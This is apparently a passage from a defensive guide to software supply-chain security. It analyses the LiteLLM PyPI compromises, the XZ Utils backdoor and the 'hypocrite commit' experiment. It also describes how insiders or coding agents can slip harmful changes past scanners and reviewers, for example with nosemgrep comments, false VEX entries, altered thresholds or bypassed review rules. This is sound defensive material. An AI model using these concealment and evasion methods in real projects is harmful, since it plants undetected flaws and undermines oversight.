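Early reports gave a different explanation for the stolen tokens. Help Net Security's *LiteLLM hit by second supply chain attack this year* (2026) reported LiteLLM's first theory, that the attacker had found the tokens in the logs of an exposed LiteLLM server, where the coding assistant Claude Code had sometimes left them. LiteLLM later said that some of its early statements were wrong or incomplete, and named the analysis by Jensen and Wang as the authoritative account.

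The package was available on PyPI from 11:39 until it was quarantined at 13:23 UTC. Wiz puts the quarantine at 13:20 and estimates about 49,000 downloads. LiteLLM's official container image was unaffected in March because it installed pinned versions of its dependencies. In October, container users were also at risk because the attacker's release replaced the image behind the tags `latest` and `main-stable` until 14:20.

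Scanning the public source code would again have missed the malware. Singh (2026), in *Compromised LiteLLM 1.107.0 on PyPI Installs a Credential Stealer and Backdoor*, compared the release with the repository file by file. The only suspicious difference in the published source archive was one added line in a build settings file, `data = "cook"`, which made the build tool copy a folder called `cook` into the finished package. The source archive didn't include that folder. The installed package had three extra files: `cook.pth`, the credential stealer it started, and `sitecustomize.py`, which contacted the attacker every hour for more code to run.

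The repository contained other warning signs. Zanki (2026), in *New Evidence Shows LiteLLM Secret-Stealing Workflows Ran 11 Days Before Supply Chain*, found that the secret-stealing jobs had run there on 10 October. Someone watching for new or changed build jobs could have had 11 days to stop the release.

The signature on the container image did not help, because LiteLLM's own pipeline had signed the image. But the build records named `Berri-AI/litellm` as the source, so a user who noticed that the real name has no hyphen could have rejected the image.

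### How malicious-package detectors work

A malicious-package detector examines a package's contents and behaviour instead of looking for an advisory. Security companies run these detectors on new releases, and some sell tools that block suspicious packages before a team installs them. Most detectors combine several signals, each of which can have a harmless cause.

| Signal | In the LiteLLM packages | A harmless cause |
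| --- | --- | --- |
| Code that runs without anyone calling it | `litellm_init.pth`, `cook.pth`, `sitecustomize.py` | Python's setuptools package also installs a `.pth` file |
| Obfuscation | Code stored as encoded text, which the package decodes and executes | Some packages store images or test data as encoded text |
| Access to credentials | Searches for SSH keys and cloud credentials | Cloud libraries have to read cloud credentials |
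| Network calls | Uploads to `models.litellm.cloud` and `www.litellm.dev` | Sending requests to outside servers is LiteLLM's job |
| Differences from the source | Files with no counterpart on GitHub | Build tools add generated files and change settings |

A detector can read a package's files without running them, or install the package on an isolated machine and record what it does. Many detectors focus on installation, because an older kind of Python package can run a setup script then. The LiteLLM malware didn't need a setup script, because pip only had to copy the files into place and the theft began the next time Python started. To trigger the malware, a sandbox test of 1.82.8 or 1.107.0 had to start a new Python process after installation, and a test of 1.82.7 had to import `proxy_server.py`.

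An engineer can make the simplest check by hand. These commands download a package without installing it, then list any files that Python would run at startup:

```
pip download litellm==1.106.2 --no-deps --only-binary=:all: -d check
unzip -l check/*.whl | grep -E '\.pth|sitecustomize\.py'
```

This check would have shown the startup files in 1.82.8 and 1.107.0 but missed 1.82.7, which hid its code in an existing file. The option `--only-binary=:all:` prevents pip from downloading source archives, since pip may run a package's setup code when it downloads one.

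Comparing a package with its source would have caught all three versions, but it takes more judgement. Singh found five edited files in the October source archive. Four of the edits only added a line naming the README file, and LiteLLM's legitimate releases have the same edits. The tag for version 1.107.0 also pointed to a commit whose settings gave the version as 1.108.0. A tool that reported every difference would probably flag most LiteLLM releases, and engineers would soon stop reading its reports.

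A team choosing a detector needs to know both its detection rate and its false-alarm rate. Suppose the ship-maintenance project takes in 2,000 new package versions a year, one of them malicious, and a detector catches 90% of malicious packages and wrongly flags 1% of harmless ones. The detector would raise about 20 false alarms a year, which would take ten hours to check at half an hour each. That is reasonable for a 90% chance of catching the malicious package. At a false-alarm rate of 20%, checking the false alarms would take 200 hours.

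These rates are only an example. The two LiteLLM attacks involved three malicious versions, which are far too few to estimate real rates. When a vendor quotes a detection rate, a reviewer should ask whether the test used malware that was already public when the vendor wrote the detector's rules, since those packages are the easiest to recognise. The team can also build a harmless package whose `.pth` file prints one word, put it on a private server and check whether the detector flags it.

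### What each defence would have done

No single defence would have stopped both attacks at every stage. Some defences protect the people who install a package, and others protect the project that publishes it.

| Defence | March 2026 | October 2026 |
| --- | --- | --- |
| Lock file with hashes | Protects users who didn't update the file during the attack | The same, but container users also have to fix the image's hash |
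| Seven-day wait | Blocks both LiteLLM versions and the new Trivy release, but not the moved trivy-action tags | Blocks the PyPI package |
| Internal mirror with an approval step | Blocks both versions if nobody approves them on the first day | Blocks the package on the same condition |
| Short-lived publishing credentials | Leave no permanent PyPI token to steal | LiteLLM already used them, and the attack succeeded |
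| Scanner without access to secrets | Leaves the poisoned Trivy nothing to steal | No effect, because the attacker didn't use a scanner |

A hash in a lock file is a checksum of the exact package the team chose. Pip refuses a file that doesn't match it, even if the name and version are right. The entry for the last release before the March attack begins like this:

```
litellm==1.82.6 \
    --hash=sha256:164a3ef3e19f309e...
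```

The ship-maintenance team can add hashes and a waiting period when it creates the lock file. On 21 October, with a wait of seven days, the commands would be:

```
uv pip compile requirements.in --generate-hashes \
  --exclude-newer 2026-10-14 -o requirements.txt
pip install --require-hashes -r requirements.txt
```

The date limit also covers transitive dependencies, which matters because many people who had never heard of LiteLLM had it installed as part of an AI agent framework. The tool treats files with no recorded upload time as unavailable, so a GPU build from a separate download site may need an exemption.

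A hash check shows that a file matches the one recorded in the lock file, but not that the file is safe. If an engineer had run the first command without a date limit at 11:00 UTC on 24 March, the lock file could have recorded the malicious package's hash, and every later installation would have checked its download against that hash.

Like a package in a hash-pinned lock file, a container image can be pinned by using its digest, a checksum that begins with `sha256:`, instead of a tag such as `latest`. Build steps on GitHub need a full commit hash. A waiting period isn't enough for them because an old tag can be moved to new code, as happened with trivy-action.

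An internal mirror is a server that stores copies of approved packages for all the team's machines to install. Some mirrors fetch and store any package on request. In March, such a mirror could have saved a copy of LiteLLM 1.82.8 and kept supplying it after PyPI removed it, so a mirror needs its own waiting period or approval step. A mirror also lets work continue during an attack. According to HackerNoon, PyPI's quarantine in March temporarily blocked every version of LiteLLM, including the safe ones.

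Short-lived publishing credentials would probably have prevented the March uploads if the scanner had run in a separate job from publishing. They failed in October because the attacker controlled the job that was entitled to receive a PyPI token, and so didn't need to steal one. The credentials useful to the attacker were the GitHub tokens, the first of which gave an agent system far more power than it needed to propose code changes.

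### Running a scanner without secrets

A vulnerability scanner has to read the files it examines and download its advisory data. It does not need the token used to publish a release, yet many teams scan and publish in the same build job because it is convenient.

The ship-maintenance team should give the scanner its own job, with no secrets and read-only access to the code. It can also cut off the scanner's network connection once the advisory data is in place:

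```
docker save ship-train:latest -o scan/image.tar
docker run --rm --network none \
  -v "$PWD/scan:/scan:ro" -v "$PWD/trivy-cache:/cache" \
  aquasec/trivy@sha256:<digest of the approved version> \
  image --input /scan/image.tar --cache-dir /cache \
  --skip-db-update --offline-scan
```

The first command saves the training image as a file. The second runs Trivy in a container that can read this file and write to its own cache, but can't connect to anything. An earlier job downloads the advisory data into the cache. Many guides instead give the scanner access to Docker's control socket so it can find images itself, but a program with that access can take over the whole machine.

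A compromised scanner running in isolation could still find a password inside the image, but it couldn't send it anywhere. It could also report that an image with serious flaws is clean. Isolation doesn't prevent that, but an occasional scan with a second tool might catch it.

The same precautions apply to any tool that runs during a build, including code formatters and test frameworks. In March, TeamPCP also attacked tools from Checkmarx, another security company. Security tools make good targets because teams often run them in environments that hold valuable credentials.

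### A seven-day wait and an urgent fix

Both malicious LiteLLM releases were on PyPI for less than two hours, so waiting one day before installing new releases would have been enough to avoid them. Waiting seven days gives people more time to find malware that doesn't crash a researcher's computer. But waiting also delays security fixes.

LiteLLM released such a fix soon after the March attack. It addressed CVE-2026-42208, an SQL injection flaw in the code that checks the gateway's access keys. The flaw lets an attacker insert commands into a database query. LiteLLM lists versions 1.81.16 to 1.83.6 as affected and 1.83.7 as the first fixed version. In March, the project had recommended version 1.82.6 or earlier as safe from the malware. A team that followed this advice and stayed on 1.82.6 would still have had the SQL injection flaw.

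Delaying upgrades may also be getting more dangerous. Jensen, Dholakia and Jaffer (2026) argue in *Introducing the LiteLLM Private Registry* that attackers with AI agents can turn a public fix into a working attack before users have upgraded. LiteLLM therefore plans to distribute fixes for its most serious vulnerabilities privately first. Users who aren't included in the private release will get the fixes at the same time as attackers.

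Skipping the waiting period occasionally adds little risk. The malicious LiteLLM versions were available on PyPI for about 144 minutes in total between January and mid-November 2026. An engineer who upgraded once, at a random moment in that period, had about a 1 in 3,000 chance of getting one. A build job that installed the newest version every hour would have had about a two-thirds chance of installing a malicious version during the March attack and would certainly have installed one during the October attack. The waiting period is therefore most valuable for automatic updates.

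For comparison, a flaw with a 30-day EPSS probability of 2.3% has about a 0.5% chance of being exploited over seven days, which is 17 times the risk of the single upgrade. If a break-in would do the same damage either way, the team should upgrade without waiting when its chance of being among the targets is more than about 1 in 17. The chance might well be higher than that for a gateway open to the internet, but probably not for one that only five engineers can reach.

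This estimate uses a package that attackers compromised twice in a year, so the risk for most packages should be lower. But it counts only malware that someone found, and an attacker could publish a malicious version while users are rushing to install a fix.

In practice, a seven-day wait seldom conflicts with the team's deadlines for fixes. It fits inside the 14-day and 60-day limits and leaves at least a week for testing if the fix comes out with the advisory. Only the three-day limit, for flaws that attackers are already using, requires an exception. The procedure could be:

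1. Confirm in an advisory database that the flaw exists and that the new version fixes it. Don't rely on the release notes, because whoever publishes a malicious package also writes those.
2. If possible, turn off the affected feature or block outside connections while checking the new version.
3. Lift the date limit for that one package, which uv allows with `--exclude-newer-package`, and leave the rest of the lock file alone.
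4. Download the package without installing it, look for startup files and compare it with the previous version.
5. Start it in an isolated container with fake credentials and see what it tries to contact.
6. Install it, and record the exception and its reason.

### After installing a malicious version

If the team finds that it installed 1.107.0, the obvious first command is the wrong one. `pip show litellm` prints the version, but pip is a Python program, so running it starts the malware again. LiteLLM advises deleting the malicious files from the shell first, then stopping the background process and rebuilding the environment. An engineer can look for the files without starting Python:

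```
find / \( -name cook.pth -o -name litellm_init.pth \) 2>/dev/null
```

A search of a machine can find nothing because the build job ran in a container that no longer exists, so the team also has to search its build logs. LiteLLM's March report includes two community scripts for this, one for GitHub and one for GitLab, but both need changes. They search only jobs that started between 08:00 and 12:44 UTC, although LiteLLM's warning covers installations until 16:00. Their search pattern also allows only one equals sign or hyphen after `litellm`, so it matches pip's usual message, `litellm-1.82.7`, but misses uv's, `litellm==1.82.7`. Changing `[=\-]` to `[=\-]+` makes the pattern match both.

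The team then has to revoke every credential that the affected machine could read, preferably from a different machine and all at once. Aqua, LiteLLM and the company that Beaumont checked all left some exposed credentials working after they learned of the problem, so the last step is to try each old credential and confirm that the service rejects it.

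## Why scanners miss deliberate changes by insiders

The attacker behind LiteLLM 1.107.0 had to steal tokens from the project's engineers before publishing anything. The ship-maintenance team's engineers already have that kind of access, and any of them could use it to make a harmful change on purpose.

Scanners can miss a deliberate change by an insider for four reasons. A new change matches no advisory. It can be valid code that breaks no rule. The code doesn't show what its author intended. The insider may also be able to edit the scanner's rules, its exceptions or the list of files it examines. These reasons don't always hold, and ordinary scans do catch some insiders.

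### A lower threshold in a data filter

Suppose the team's data filter gives each page a reliability score from 0 to 1 and discards the pages that score too low. Most manuals from engine makers score above 0.9, while retyped copies and forum posts score lower. One engineer makes this change, with the message "Keep more pages about older engines":

```diff
-MIN_SCORE = 0.80
+MIN_SCORE = 0.65
```

The message is accurate, since many of the pages that score between 0.65 and 0.80 are about older engines. But the engineer knows that some of those pages give wrong torque values. The next model trains on them and may repeat the wrong values to mechanics.

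None of the five kinds of scanner would report the change:

| Scanner | Why it reports nothing |
| --- | --- |
| Dependency scanner | The lock file is the same, so there is no new package or version to look up |
| Static analysis | Comparing a score with a number is not a faulty pattern, and the change sends no data to a dangerous function |
| Secret scanner | 0.65 doesn't have the format of a key and isn't a long random string |
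| Configuration and container scanner | The filter runs in the same container with the same permissions |
| Model-file scanner | The new weights differ from the old ones only in their numbers, and the file contains no code |

The team's data checks are also unlikely to catch the change. The raw files still match their checksums because the engineer changed only the filter. A distribution check might show that the training set has grown, but the engineer has already explained the growth in the message.

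A rule that reports every change to `MIN_SCORE` would flag this one, but it would also flag honest adjustments. A team with too few pages about older engines might be better off with 0.65. Whether the change does harm depends on what the extra pages contain, which a scanner that reads only the code can't check.

### How a maintainer hid a backdoor in XZ Utils

XZ Utils is a set of compression tools that many Linux systems include. In February 2024, one of its two maintainers released a version with a backdoor that let an attacker run commands without logging in on some Linux machines that accept remote connections over SSH. Dependency scanners had no advisory to match that version against for nearly five weeks.

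The maintainer used the name Jia Tan, which is probably false. *Timeline of the xz open source attack* (2024) dates their first patch, a harmless one, to October 2021. Lasse Collin, who then ran XZ Utils alone as an unpaid hobby, was short of time and had long-term mental health problems. In the spring of 2022, two people complained on the project's mailing list about slow progress and urged him to hand the project over to someone else. Their email addresses appear almost nowhere else on the internet, so both people were probably invented to pressure him. By the end of 2022, Jia Tan could merge code without asking, and published their first release in March 2023.

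Jia Tan put most of the backdoor in the project's repository on 23 February 2024, disguised as two compressed test files. The project already had many such files, and its documentation explained that some were handmade and had no readable source. Reviewers therefore had little reason to expect the new ones to be readable.

The test files did nothing by themselves. The next day, Jia Tan published version 5.6.0 as an archive containing a build script with one extra line. That line started a chain of commands that extracted the hidden code and built it into the XZ library. Freund (2024), in *backdoor in upstream xz/liblzma leading to ssh server compromise*, reported that the line was missing from the repository. It took effect only during the build of a Debian or RPM package on 64-bit x86 Linux. A static analysis tool that read the repository would have found no trigger, just as it would have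 found no malware in LiteLLM's repository.

Andres Freund, a developer who describes himself as "*not* a security researcher", discovered the backdoor after noticing that SSH logins on his Debian machines used a lot of processor time and that Valgrind, a tool that checks programs for memory errors, was reporting problems in the XZ library. In his test, a refused login took 0.807 seconds with the backdoor and 0.299 seconds without it. He notified Debian and other distributions on 28 March, and Red Hat assigned CVE-2024-3094, after which dependency scanners could find the affected versions.

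Others had seen the Valgrind errors in early March. Jia Tan answered with a false fix, then replaced the two test files and published version 5.6.1. Freund considered whether an outsider had taken over Jia Tan's computer, but thought this less likely because Jia Tan had discussed the supposed fixes on several mailing lists.

### Valid patches with a missing piece

Some deliberate flaws do break a rule that a scanner can check. In November 2021, Jia Tan sent libarchive a change that replaced the function `safe_fprintf` with the less secure `fprintf`. According to *On the critical path to implant backdoors* (2024), the project merged it without noticing that it might be suspicious. A pattern rule that reports new calls to `fprintf` would have flagged it. It is still uncertain whether the change was related to the XZ Utils backdoor.

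An insider can avoid many such rules by letting old code supply most of the flaw. Qiushi Wu and Kangjie Lu of the University of Minnesota tried this on the Linux kernel in August 2020. Wu and Lu (2020), in *Clarifications on the “hypocrite commit” work (FAQ)*, describe the procedure:

1. They used static analysis to find three "immature vulnerabilities", places in the kernel where all but one of the conditions for a vulnerability were already present. The missing condition might be the use of a piece of memory after the program has released it.
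2. They found three real but minor bugs whose repair could supply the missing conditions.
3. They emailed the kernel's developers three repairs, each under five lines long, that introduced those conditions.
4. When a maintainer replied that a patch looked good, they pointed out the flaw, asked the maintainer not to apply the patch and sent a correct one.

Each patch had a plausible purpose, and a reviewer who looked only at the changed lines could easily approve it. Static analysis can still help here. The researchers used it to find the weak places, and they suggest that maintainers look for them too. A tool can search for memory being used after it is released because that is an error in any program, but no general rule defines a wrong value of `MIN_SCORE`.

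Accounts of the experiment differ. Wu and Lu describe three flawed patches. The University of Minnesota's *Statement from Computer Science & Engineering confirming Linux Technical Advisory Board findings* (2021) lists four patches, one of them valid, and reports that none got past review. A timeline by the Linux Foundation's advisory board, which Machek (2021) quotes on the kernel's mailing list, lists five messages sent under false identities. None of these accounts makes clear how many flaws the reviewers noticed themselves and how many the researchers had to reveal. The experiment therefore doesn't give a miss rate for human review, and a rate based on three or four patches would be very rough anyway.

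The experiment also led to a dispute about consent. Other security researchers wrote to the conference that had accepted the paper, objecting that it involved experiments on human subjects (*Ethics concerns about paper accepted for publication*). Wu and Lu answered that they had studied a process, not individuals. They had a letter from the university's ethics board exempting the work, but admitted that they hadn't applied for approval at the start. They withdrew the paper in April 2021 because they had wasted the developers' time without their knowledge or permission (Wu and Lu, 2021).

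### Honest mistakes that look deliberate

The dispute that followed in Linux is better evidence about intent than the experiment itself. In April 2021, the kernel developer Greg Kroah-Hartman banned the whole university from contributing and told other developers that it had submitted its patches in bad faith. Machek objected that there had been no deception in 2021. Cook (2021), a member of the advisory board, agreed that the wording should have distinguished malicious changes from valid fixes. The university says its researchers sent that April's five patches in good faith, although the patches were superfluous and of poor quality.

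Kernel developers then checked 435 earlier changes linked to the university. According to Tom's Hardware's *Linux Foundation Issues Frosty Final Judgment in UMN Scandal*, 349 were correct, 39 were wrong and still needed fixing, and later changes had already fixed another 25. At least 64 changes, about one in seven, were therefore faulty. If the university is right that all its earlier patches were honest, a reviewer who treated every flaw as a sign of malice would have been wrong about all 64. The work was also slow, and the board thanked 85 developers for helping, according to a reader's comment on LWN's *The TAB report on the UMN affair* (2021).

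Participants at an industry meeting described in *S3C2 Summit 2025-03* (2025) also found it hard to tell bugs from malicious intent, and some said they assume any commit could be malicious.

A scanner doesn't always need to know the intent behind a flaw. If it finds a way to run commands through a file name, the team should fix the flaw regardless of who put it there or why. In a few cases, the code itself is strong evidence of intent. XZ's build script decoded a damaged-looking test file and ran the result as commands, which has no plausible innocent purpose. Intent matters most when the harm is uncertain, as it is with the filter's threshold, and when the team has to decide whether to recheck everything else the same person wrote.

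### Changing what the scanner examines

Jia Tan also controlled some of XZ's testing. The project used OSS-Fuzz, a free Google service for fuzzing, which means running a program on many automatically varied inputs to see whether it fails. In March 2023, Jia Tan arranged to receive the service's bug reports. In July, they turned off an XZ feature in the versions that OSS-Fuzz tested, and the backdoor later used that feature to take control of other programs. *Timeline of the xz open source attack* cautions that the July change may have been innocent.

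An engineer on the ship-maintenance team could do something similar with less effort. A comment such as `# nosemgrep` makes Semgrep ignore a line, a false VEX statement can hide a known vulnerability, and an extra entry in an ignore file can exclude a folder from the scan. The build still passes, and the report looks the same as one for clean code.

An engineer who wants the scanner to ignore a flaw needs permission to edit its settings, or has to persuade someone who has that permission. Changes to the settings also remain in the version history, where a new exception may attract more attention than the flaw it hides. The engineer who lowered `MIN_SCORE` did not need to take that risk, because no scanner reported the change.

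### The intern at ByteDance

The best-known accusation of this kind in AI development concerns ByteDance, the Chinese company that owns TikTok. In October 2024, after rumours spread on Chinese social media, the company confirmed that it had dismissed an intern that August. ByteDance said in a statement, quoted in Tech.co's *TikTok Parent ByteDance Fired an Intern for Sabotaging AI Training*, that he had "maliciously interfered with the model training tasks" of a research project. He was on the company's advertising technology team, according to Chen's *ByteDance terminates intern for sabotaging project, dismisses reports on losses*.

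ByteDance denied that the intern had disrupted a system of more than 8,000 graphics processors and called reports of losses in the millions of dollars "grossly exaggerated", according to International Business Times' *TikTok Owner Fires Intern For Sabotaging AI Research, Downplays Damage*. Lv reports in *TikTok Owner ByteDance Confirms Intern Sabotaged AI Model Training* that the company said neither the project nor its businesses had been harmed. Lv treats the story that the intern used malware from Hugging Face as a rumour.

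A month later, ByteDance sued him. It sought 8 million yuan for losses, 20,000 yuan for expenses, and a public apology, according to Xu (2024) in *ByteDance Seeks Over USD1.1 Million From Ex-Intern*. The claim for losses is hard to reconcile with the company's earlier statement that the incident had no impact. According to a Chinese newspaper report that Chen cites, the lawsuit accused him of tampering with code, and a Beijing court accepted the case. This does not mean the court found the accusation true.

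The company's confirmation makes it reasonable to plan for insiders who interfere with training. But it doesn't help us judge scanners, because outsiders don't have the code the intern allegedly changed and so can't test scanners on it.

### Insiders whom ordinary scans catch

An insider who copies known malware takes a large risk, because antivirus programs and malicious-package detectors can recognise it. For example, Collin writes on *xz backdoor*, Tukaani's page about the incident, that antivirus software now complains about XZ's test files, although they are harmless without the build script. Jia Tan used those files without setting off an alarm, but anyone who reused them today would probably set one off.

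Dependency scanners can catch an insider who brings back an old flaw. Suppose an engineer downgrades PyTorch from 2.6.0 to 2.5.1, planning to exploit CVE-2025-32434 with a prepared model file. The scanner reports the flaw just as it would if someone had forgotten to upgrade. Whoever handles the alert should look up who downgraded PyTorch and ask why, since upgrading it again would remove the flaw but leave the engineer free to try something else.

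Secret scanners find credentials whether someone committed them deliberately or by accident. An insider might save a cloud key in an old notebook to keep access after leaving the company, and the scanner will report the key if it has a known format. Careless insiders' mistakes are even easier to catch. They turn off weights-only loading to get past an error, or pass a file name to the shell because it is quicker, and static analysis has rules for detecting both.

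All of these insiders did something that an honest engineer might also do by accident, or that another attacker had already done.

### One malicious change in 10,000

Some detectors look for signs of malice in each code change instead of a known flaw. They face the same problem of rare cases as the scanners for backdoored models. Consider a company whose engineers make 10,000 changes a year, one of them malicious, and a detector that catches 80% of malicious changes and wrongly flags 5% of harmless ones. The chance that a flagged change is malicious is:

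P = d·m / (d·m + f·(N − m))

Here N is the number of changes, m the number of malicious ones, d the detection rate and f the false-alarm rate. The detector raises about 500 false alarms a year (0.05 × 9,999) and flags an average of 0.8 malicious changes. About 0.16% of flagged changes (0.8 / 500.75), or roughly one in 626, are therefore malicious.

A flagged change is 16 times as likely to be malicious as one picked at random, but the company would have to check two false alarms every working day. At half an hour each, that takes 250 hours a year. The reviewer also has to recognise the malicious change after months in which every alarm was false. If the reviewer has an even chance of recognising it, the company's chance of stopping the change falls from 80% to 40%.

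| Changes examined | Malicious | Detection rate | False-alarm rate | False alarms a year | Flagged changes that are malicious |
| --- | --- | --- | --- | --- | --- |
| 10,000 | 1 | 80% | 5% | 500 | 0.16% |
| 10,000 | 1 | 100% | 5% | 500 | 0.20% |
| 10,000 | 10 | 80% | 5% | 500 | 1.6% |
| 10,000 | 1 | 80% | 0.5% | 50 | 1.6% |
| 200 | 1 | 80% | 5% | 10 | 7.4% |
| 200 | 1 | 80% | 0.5% | 1 | 45% |

Lowering the false-alarm rate greatly increases the share of alarms that are correct, while even perfect detection would barely change it. For half of the alarms to be correct, the detector could flag no more than one in 12,500 harmless changes.

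The company can also examine fewer changes. The last two rows show the result if 200 changes a year affect the data filters, the evaluation code or the release jobs, and the malicious change is one of them. Even the 5% detector then takes only about five hours a year. But an insider who knows which files are checked can choose a different one. Few companies would have chosen to check XZ's folder of compressed test files.

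### A detector that watches programs run

In *Not In My Git Yard*, Kokkonis, Marcozzi and Zacchiroli (2026) report that their tool, Lily, has a false-alarm rate low enough for daily use. Lily fuzzes the new version of a program for ten minutes and records which types of system call it makes. A system call is a request to the operating system, such as to open a file or start another program.

Lily flags an input only if the new version responds with a set of system calls that it never produced on the test inputs saved from earlier rounds, and the old version does not produce the same set for that input. The first condition keeps Lily from flagging new features that the saved inputs already exercise, and the second keeps it from flagging odd behaviour that was there before the change.

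The method suits backdoors like the one that attackers put into vsFTPd, a file server. Anyone who entered ":)" as a user name got a remote command line with full control of the machine. Opening that command line takes system calls that an ordinary login doesn't need, so the backdoor stands out if the fuzzer happens to try that name. Lily then shows the reviewer the changed lines involved, usually fewer than a dozen.

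In tests on 432 safe and 13 backdoored commits, Lily detected 90% of the backdoors on average and wrongly flagged 0.2% of the safe commits. At those rates, the company with 10,000 changes would get about 20 false alarms a year, and one in 23 flagged changes would be malicious. Checking the flagged changes would take about ten hours. On whole releases, which combine many changes, Lily detected 83% of the backdoors and wrongly flagged 4.3% of the safe releases.

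Thirteen backdoored commits are a small sample, and some of the backdoors were synthetic. The researchers think Lily would probably have prevented three real attacks, on vsFTPd, ProFTPD and PHP. The three don't include XZ, whose backdoor ran only inside the SSH server, so fuzzing the compression tools alone would not have triggered it. The researchers examined five ways to evade Lily, including bypassing the automated tests and adding the backdoor's behaviour to the saved inputs so that it counts as normal. They concluded that evasion takes substantial effort and may still fail, and they offer a hardened mode that protects the saved inputs.

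Lily would miss the lower threshold in the data filter. With `MIN_SCORE` at 0.65, the filter opens the same input files and writes the same output file as before, but with more pages in it. Kokkonis and colleagues argue that any meaningful backdoor in code has to make system calls. The filter does make system calls, but it writes the harmful pages using a call that it always makes.

A language model might do better, because it can work out what the threshold is for. But the models in Pellew and Raza's test were looking for recognised types of security flaw, which they could find in the code itself. To judge the threshold, a model or a person would have to read the pages that the change lets in and know the correct torque values.

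### Coding agents with commit rights

AI models now write much of the code at some AI companies. Anthropic (2026) reported in *When AI builds itself* that its model Claude wrote more than 80% of the code the company merged in May 2026, up from a low single-digit percentage before February 2025. This figure is self-reported and doesn't measure how carefully anyone reviewed the code.

Some coding agents can also commit changes, which gives them an insider's access. LiteLLM's agents had even more access because their token had all of an owner's permissions. An agent with insider access could lower `MIN_SCORE` as easily as an engineer could, and the scanners would not flag that change either.

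The agent's reasons may be even harder to establish than a person's. It might have followed instructions that an outsider hid in a document, or loosened the filter because its task was to produce a larger training set. Similarly, an agent told to make a failing build pass might add a scanner exception. The commit could look identical in every case, and the agent's later explanation may not be accurate.

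Agents also increase the number of changes. If they raise the company's total from 10,000 to 30,000 a year and there is still only one malicious change, the detector with a 5% false-alarm rate will produce about 1,500 false alarms, and only 0.05% of flagged changes will be malicious. If agents make harmful changes more often than people do, a larger share of the alarms will be correct, but the company will still have about 1,500 false ones to check.

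## Checks that can catch an insider's change

No scanner reported that the engineer had lowered `MIN_SCORE` from 0.80 to 0.65. But other people and systems can still check the change before it reaches a released model.

### Approval by a second person

The earliest check is code review, in which a colleague reads and approves a change before it joins the main version of the code. Review can reveal a change that makes no sense, and it stops an engineer from acting alone. SLSA (Supply-chain Levels for Software Artifacts, an industry specification for protecting software from tampering) gives the example of SushiSwap, a cryptocurrency exchange, where a contractor with access to the code added a change that redirected money to themself, which a second reviewer could have caught.

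Review takes a lot of time. At ten minutes each, a company's 10,000 changes a year would take almost 1,700 hours, about one engineer's working year. An insider can also get around a carelessly designed rule in several ways that SLSA describes:

| Way around the rule | Countermeasure |
| --- | --- |
| Edit the change after a colleague approves it | Cancel approvals whenever the change is modified |
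| Approve it from a second account or through a bot | Don't let bots approve changes, and record who controls each one |
| Hide a program in a file type that needs no review, such as `help.md` | Remove the exemption |
| Add a harmful commit, then undo it in the same proposal so that the reviewer sees no difference | Merge each proposal as a single commit, which keeps the harmful one out of the main history |
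| Turn off the rule, make the change and turn the rule back on | Require a second person for changes to the rule, and log them |

SLSA says it doesn't currently address collusion between two trusted people, harmful changes that look benign, or reviewers who approve without reading. A team can require more reviewers or more senior ones, but each addition helps less than the last. A thief with two people's credentials can also defeat two-person approval.

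Coding agents create another gap, because an engineer can tell an agent to write a change and then approve it without involving anyone else. SLSA's *Source* requirements call for two trusted people, but they let a team permanently exempt a trusted bot, such as Dependabot. SLSA's list of threats recommends two human reviewers even for changes that bots write, which is the safer rule for any agent that takes instructions from engineers.

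### Protected branches and separate owners

A protected branch is a line of development that people can change only under rules enforced by the hosting service. These rules require approval for changes and preserve the branch's history. Without them, an engineer could publish a release from a harmful commit and then overwrite the branch to erase the commit.

Protection has few drawbacks besides slower emergency fixes, but an administrator can turn it off. SLSA therefore treats a rule as continuous only since someone last turned it on. Whenever a rule changes, the ship-maintenance team should alert someone who can't edit the rules.

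The team also needs to decide whose approval counts. On GitHub, a file called `CODEOWNERS` assigns reviewers to parts of a repository:

```
/filters/             @ship/data-reviewers
/scanner/             @ship/security
/.github/             @ship/security
```

If the `scanner` folder holds the rules, ignore files and VEX statements, an engineer can't add an exception without approval from the security group. The `CODEOWNERS` file should also be in a protected folder, here `.github`, because otherwise an insider could change the owners first. The team also has to turn on the setting that requires an owner's approval.

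File ownership doesn't cover a `# nosemgrep` comment in ordinary code, but running Semgrep with `--disable-nosem` reports the finding despite the comment. For a team of five, the main drawback of file ownership is waiting for the right reviewer, who may have to come from another department. File ownership fails as a check if that reviewer is the insider, or if someone can change the scanner's settings on the vendor's website.

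### Builds on a system that no developer controls

An engineer who builds a release on a laptop can add anything to it after the review. A build service can instead build the release on a clean machine, using code from the protected branch, and delete the machine afterwards. This prevents unreviewed edits during the build but doesn't show whether the reviewed code is safe.

Engineers often log in to training machines to find out why a run is slow or has crashed. The team could allow this for experiments and mark a run as unfit for release if anyone logged in to its machines. An administrator of the build service, or an outsider with the administrator's credentials, can still tamper with a build.

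### What a provenance record contains

A provenance record is a signed statement of which source, build system and inputs produced a file. A simplified record for the ship-maintenance model might look like this:

```json
{
  "subject": [{"name": "ship-model.safetensors",
               "digest": {"sha256": "9b2e..."}}],
  "predicate": {
    "buildDefinition": {
      "buildType": "train-release-v1",
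      "externalParameters": {
        "repository": "ship-team/ship-model",
        "branch": "main",
        "config": "release.yaml"},
      "resolvedDependencies": [
        {"name": "source", "digest": {"gitCommit": "41d7..."}},
        {"name": "training-set", "digest": {"sha256": "c05a..."}},
        {"name": "base-model", "digest": {"sha256": "77f1..."}}]},
    "runDetails": {"builder": {"id": "release-builder"}}
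  }
}
```

The build service writes the record, which includes the model file's checksum, and signs it with a key that the engineers can't use. Any change to the record invalidates the signature, and a model file that has been changed no longer matches the recorded checksum.

SLSA's *Build* guidance warns that "provenance doesn't do anything unless somebody inspects it". Before publishing the model, a separate job should do the following:

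1. Check the signature against a list of trusted build services and their keys.
2. Calculate the model file's checksum and compare it with the one under `subject`.
3. Compare the build service, source repository, build type and parameters with the expected values. Reject any parameter that isn't on the list.
4. Check the dependencies, including the training set, against the approved versions.

The third step catches a release that the right service built from the wrong code, for example from `evilfork/my-package` instead of `good/my-package`. The expected values need protection too, because an insider who could edit them could make the wrong repository pass. SLSA suggests requiring two people to change these values.

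A provenance record proves where a file came from, but not that the source was harmless. If a colleague approves the lower threshold, the record will be accurate and every check will pass. SLSA's advice on what to compare assumes an attacker who can start builds and publish packages but can't change the source. Once someone finds a wrong torque value, the team can use the record to identify every model it trained with the altered filter.

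The fourth step is optional in SLSA, which doesn't require the list of dependencies to be complete. A record that left out the training data could therefore still qualify for the highest build level, so an AI team has to set its own rule that training data must be listed.

### The SLSA levels in 2026

SLSA (2025) released version 1.2 in November 2025. It added a track for source code to the existing one for builds:

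| Level | Source track | Build track |
| --- | --- | --- |
| 0 | No assurance | No assurance |
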